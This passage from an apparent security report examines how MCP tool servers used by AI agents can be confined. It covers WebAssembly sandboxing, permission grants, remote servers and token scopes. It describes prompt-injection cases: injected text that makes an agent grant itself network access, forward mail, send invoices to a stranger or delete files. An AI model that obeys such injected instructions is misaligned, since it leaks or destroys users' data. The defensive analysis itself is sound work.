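If the component tries to contact any other host, the attempt fails and Wassette can log it. Users have to trust Wassette and Wasmtime, the WebAssembly runtime underneath it.

The main drawback of running tools as WebAssembly is that developers have to rewrite their servers, as Microsoft's *What is Wassette?* acknowledges. The tool-testing system in *MCP-SandboxScan* has the same limitation. It can contain tools that run as WebAssembly, but *MCP-SandboxScan* recommends a separate operating-system sandbox for ordinary MCP servers. Containers are therefore more practical for most existing tools.

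Wassette's sandbox is strict, but the way users grant permissions can weaken it. Microsoft's *Managing Permissions* recommends asking the agent in ordinary language to grant a permission, and the agent then calls a tool such as grant-network-permission. Injected text could lead the agent to call the same tool. A confirmation prompt in the host might stop this, but most of the hosts that Yao and colleagues examined don't show one by default. Granting permissions from the command line is safer if the agent can't access the command line or the policy files.

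Inconvenience also leads users to grant broad access. Microsoft notes that models sometimes need a reminder to "please fix the permission errors", and a user who types this lets the model decide how much access to request. The documentation advises against wildcards, but its list of commonly used domains includes `*.amazonaws.com`, which covers storage that anyone can rent. A malicious tool with access to that domain could send stolen data to the attacker's account.

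Narrow permissions mean more prompts for users. AgentBound prompts users on every run for permissions that change often, such as the folder to work in, and people who see many prompts tend to approve them without much thought. AgentBound reduces the number of prompts by letting developers put fixed permissions, such as a single web address, in the manifest for others to import. An organisation could also have one person set the permissions for everybody, so that ordinary users never see a prompt.

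### Servers run by someone else

A host can't sandbox a server that runs on another company's machine. In August 2026, 49.7% of the servers in the official registry were available only as remote services, according to Afsar. The host can decide which credentials and data to send to such a server, but it can't control what the server does with them.

*MCP-DPT* (Rostamzadeh, Narula and colleagues, 2026) classifies attacks by which part of an MCP system can stop them. It finds that existing defences concentrate on tools and leave gaps in the host, the network connection and the supply chain. For a remote server, the useful enforcer is often the service that holds the user's data. Suppose an outside company runs search_mail, and the user's mail provider gives the company a token that only allows reading one folder. The provider will refuse a request to delete a message or open another folder,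 even if the company is dishonest.

The company can still copy everything in that folder, and revoking the token later doesn't delete the copies. If the company that runs the server also holds the data, as Abyssale does, the token's scope limits what a misled agent can do but doesn't protect the data from the company.

Scopes are also often too coarse for the user's purpose. *Access Control for Agentic AI* (Wei and Xiong, 2026) gives the example of a rule that allows an agent to send one summary to Alice. The agent's credential records only that it may send mail, and the mail service checks only that the credential is valid. Each step works correctly, but none checks that the message is the summary or that it goes to Alice.

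Some remote servers don't check credentials properly. Wei and Xiong cite a measurement of 7,973 live remote servers in which about 41% offered tools without any authentication. Missing authentication may be harmless for a tool that looks up the weather. More worryingly, the researchers tested 119 servers that used OAuth, the usual system for granting scoped tokens, and found at least one authentication flaw in every one.

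The host can also check each call before it leaves. However, *From Tool Connection to Execution Control* (2026) notes that such checks can't inspect sensitive content, such as a confidential message copied into a search query, when it travels as an ordinary argument to an authorised destination.

### The office assistant under confinement

In the second variant of the example, search_mail secretly forwards mail. If the tool runs in a container on the user's machine that can contact only the mail provider, it can't send the copy to an outside machine.

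The author could then try to email the copy out through the mail provider, as postmark-mcp did through Postmark. The allowlist permits that connection, so the mailbox credential has to be read-only as well. With both limits in place and no access to other credentials, the tool can't send the mail anywhere itself, but it can still return text that leads the model to send the mail with another tool. If search_mail runs on its author's server instead, the container and the allowlist can't confine it, and the author can keep a copy of every message the credential can open.

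Confining the tool helps much less in the first variant, where injected text makes the model send invoices to a stranger. The send_mail tool needs a connection to the mail provider and a credential that can send mail, and emailing the stranger requires the same access as emailing Maria.

If the hidden instruction is to delete files, the container can limit the damage. A delete_file tool that can write only to the drafts folder can't delete the company's accounts, but the user may still lose the drafts.
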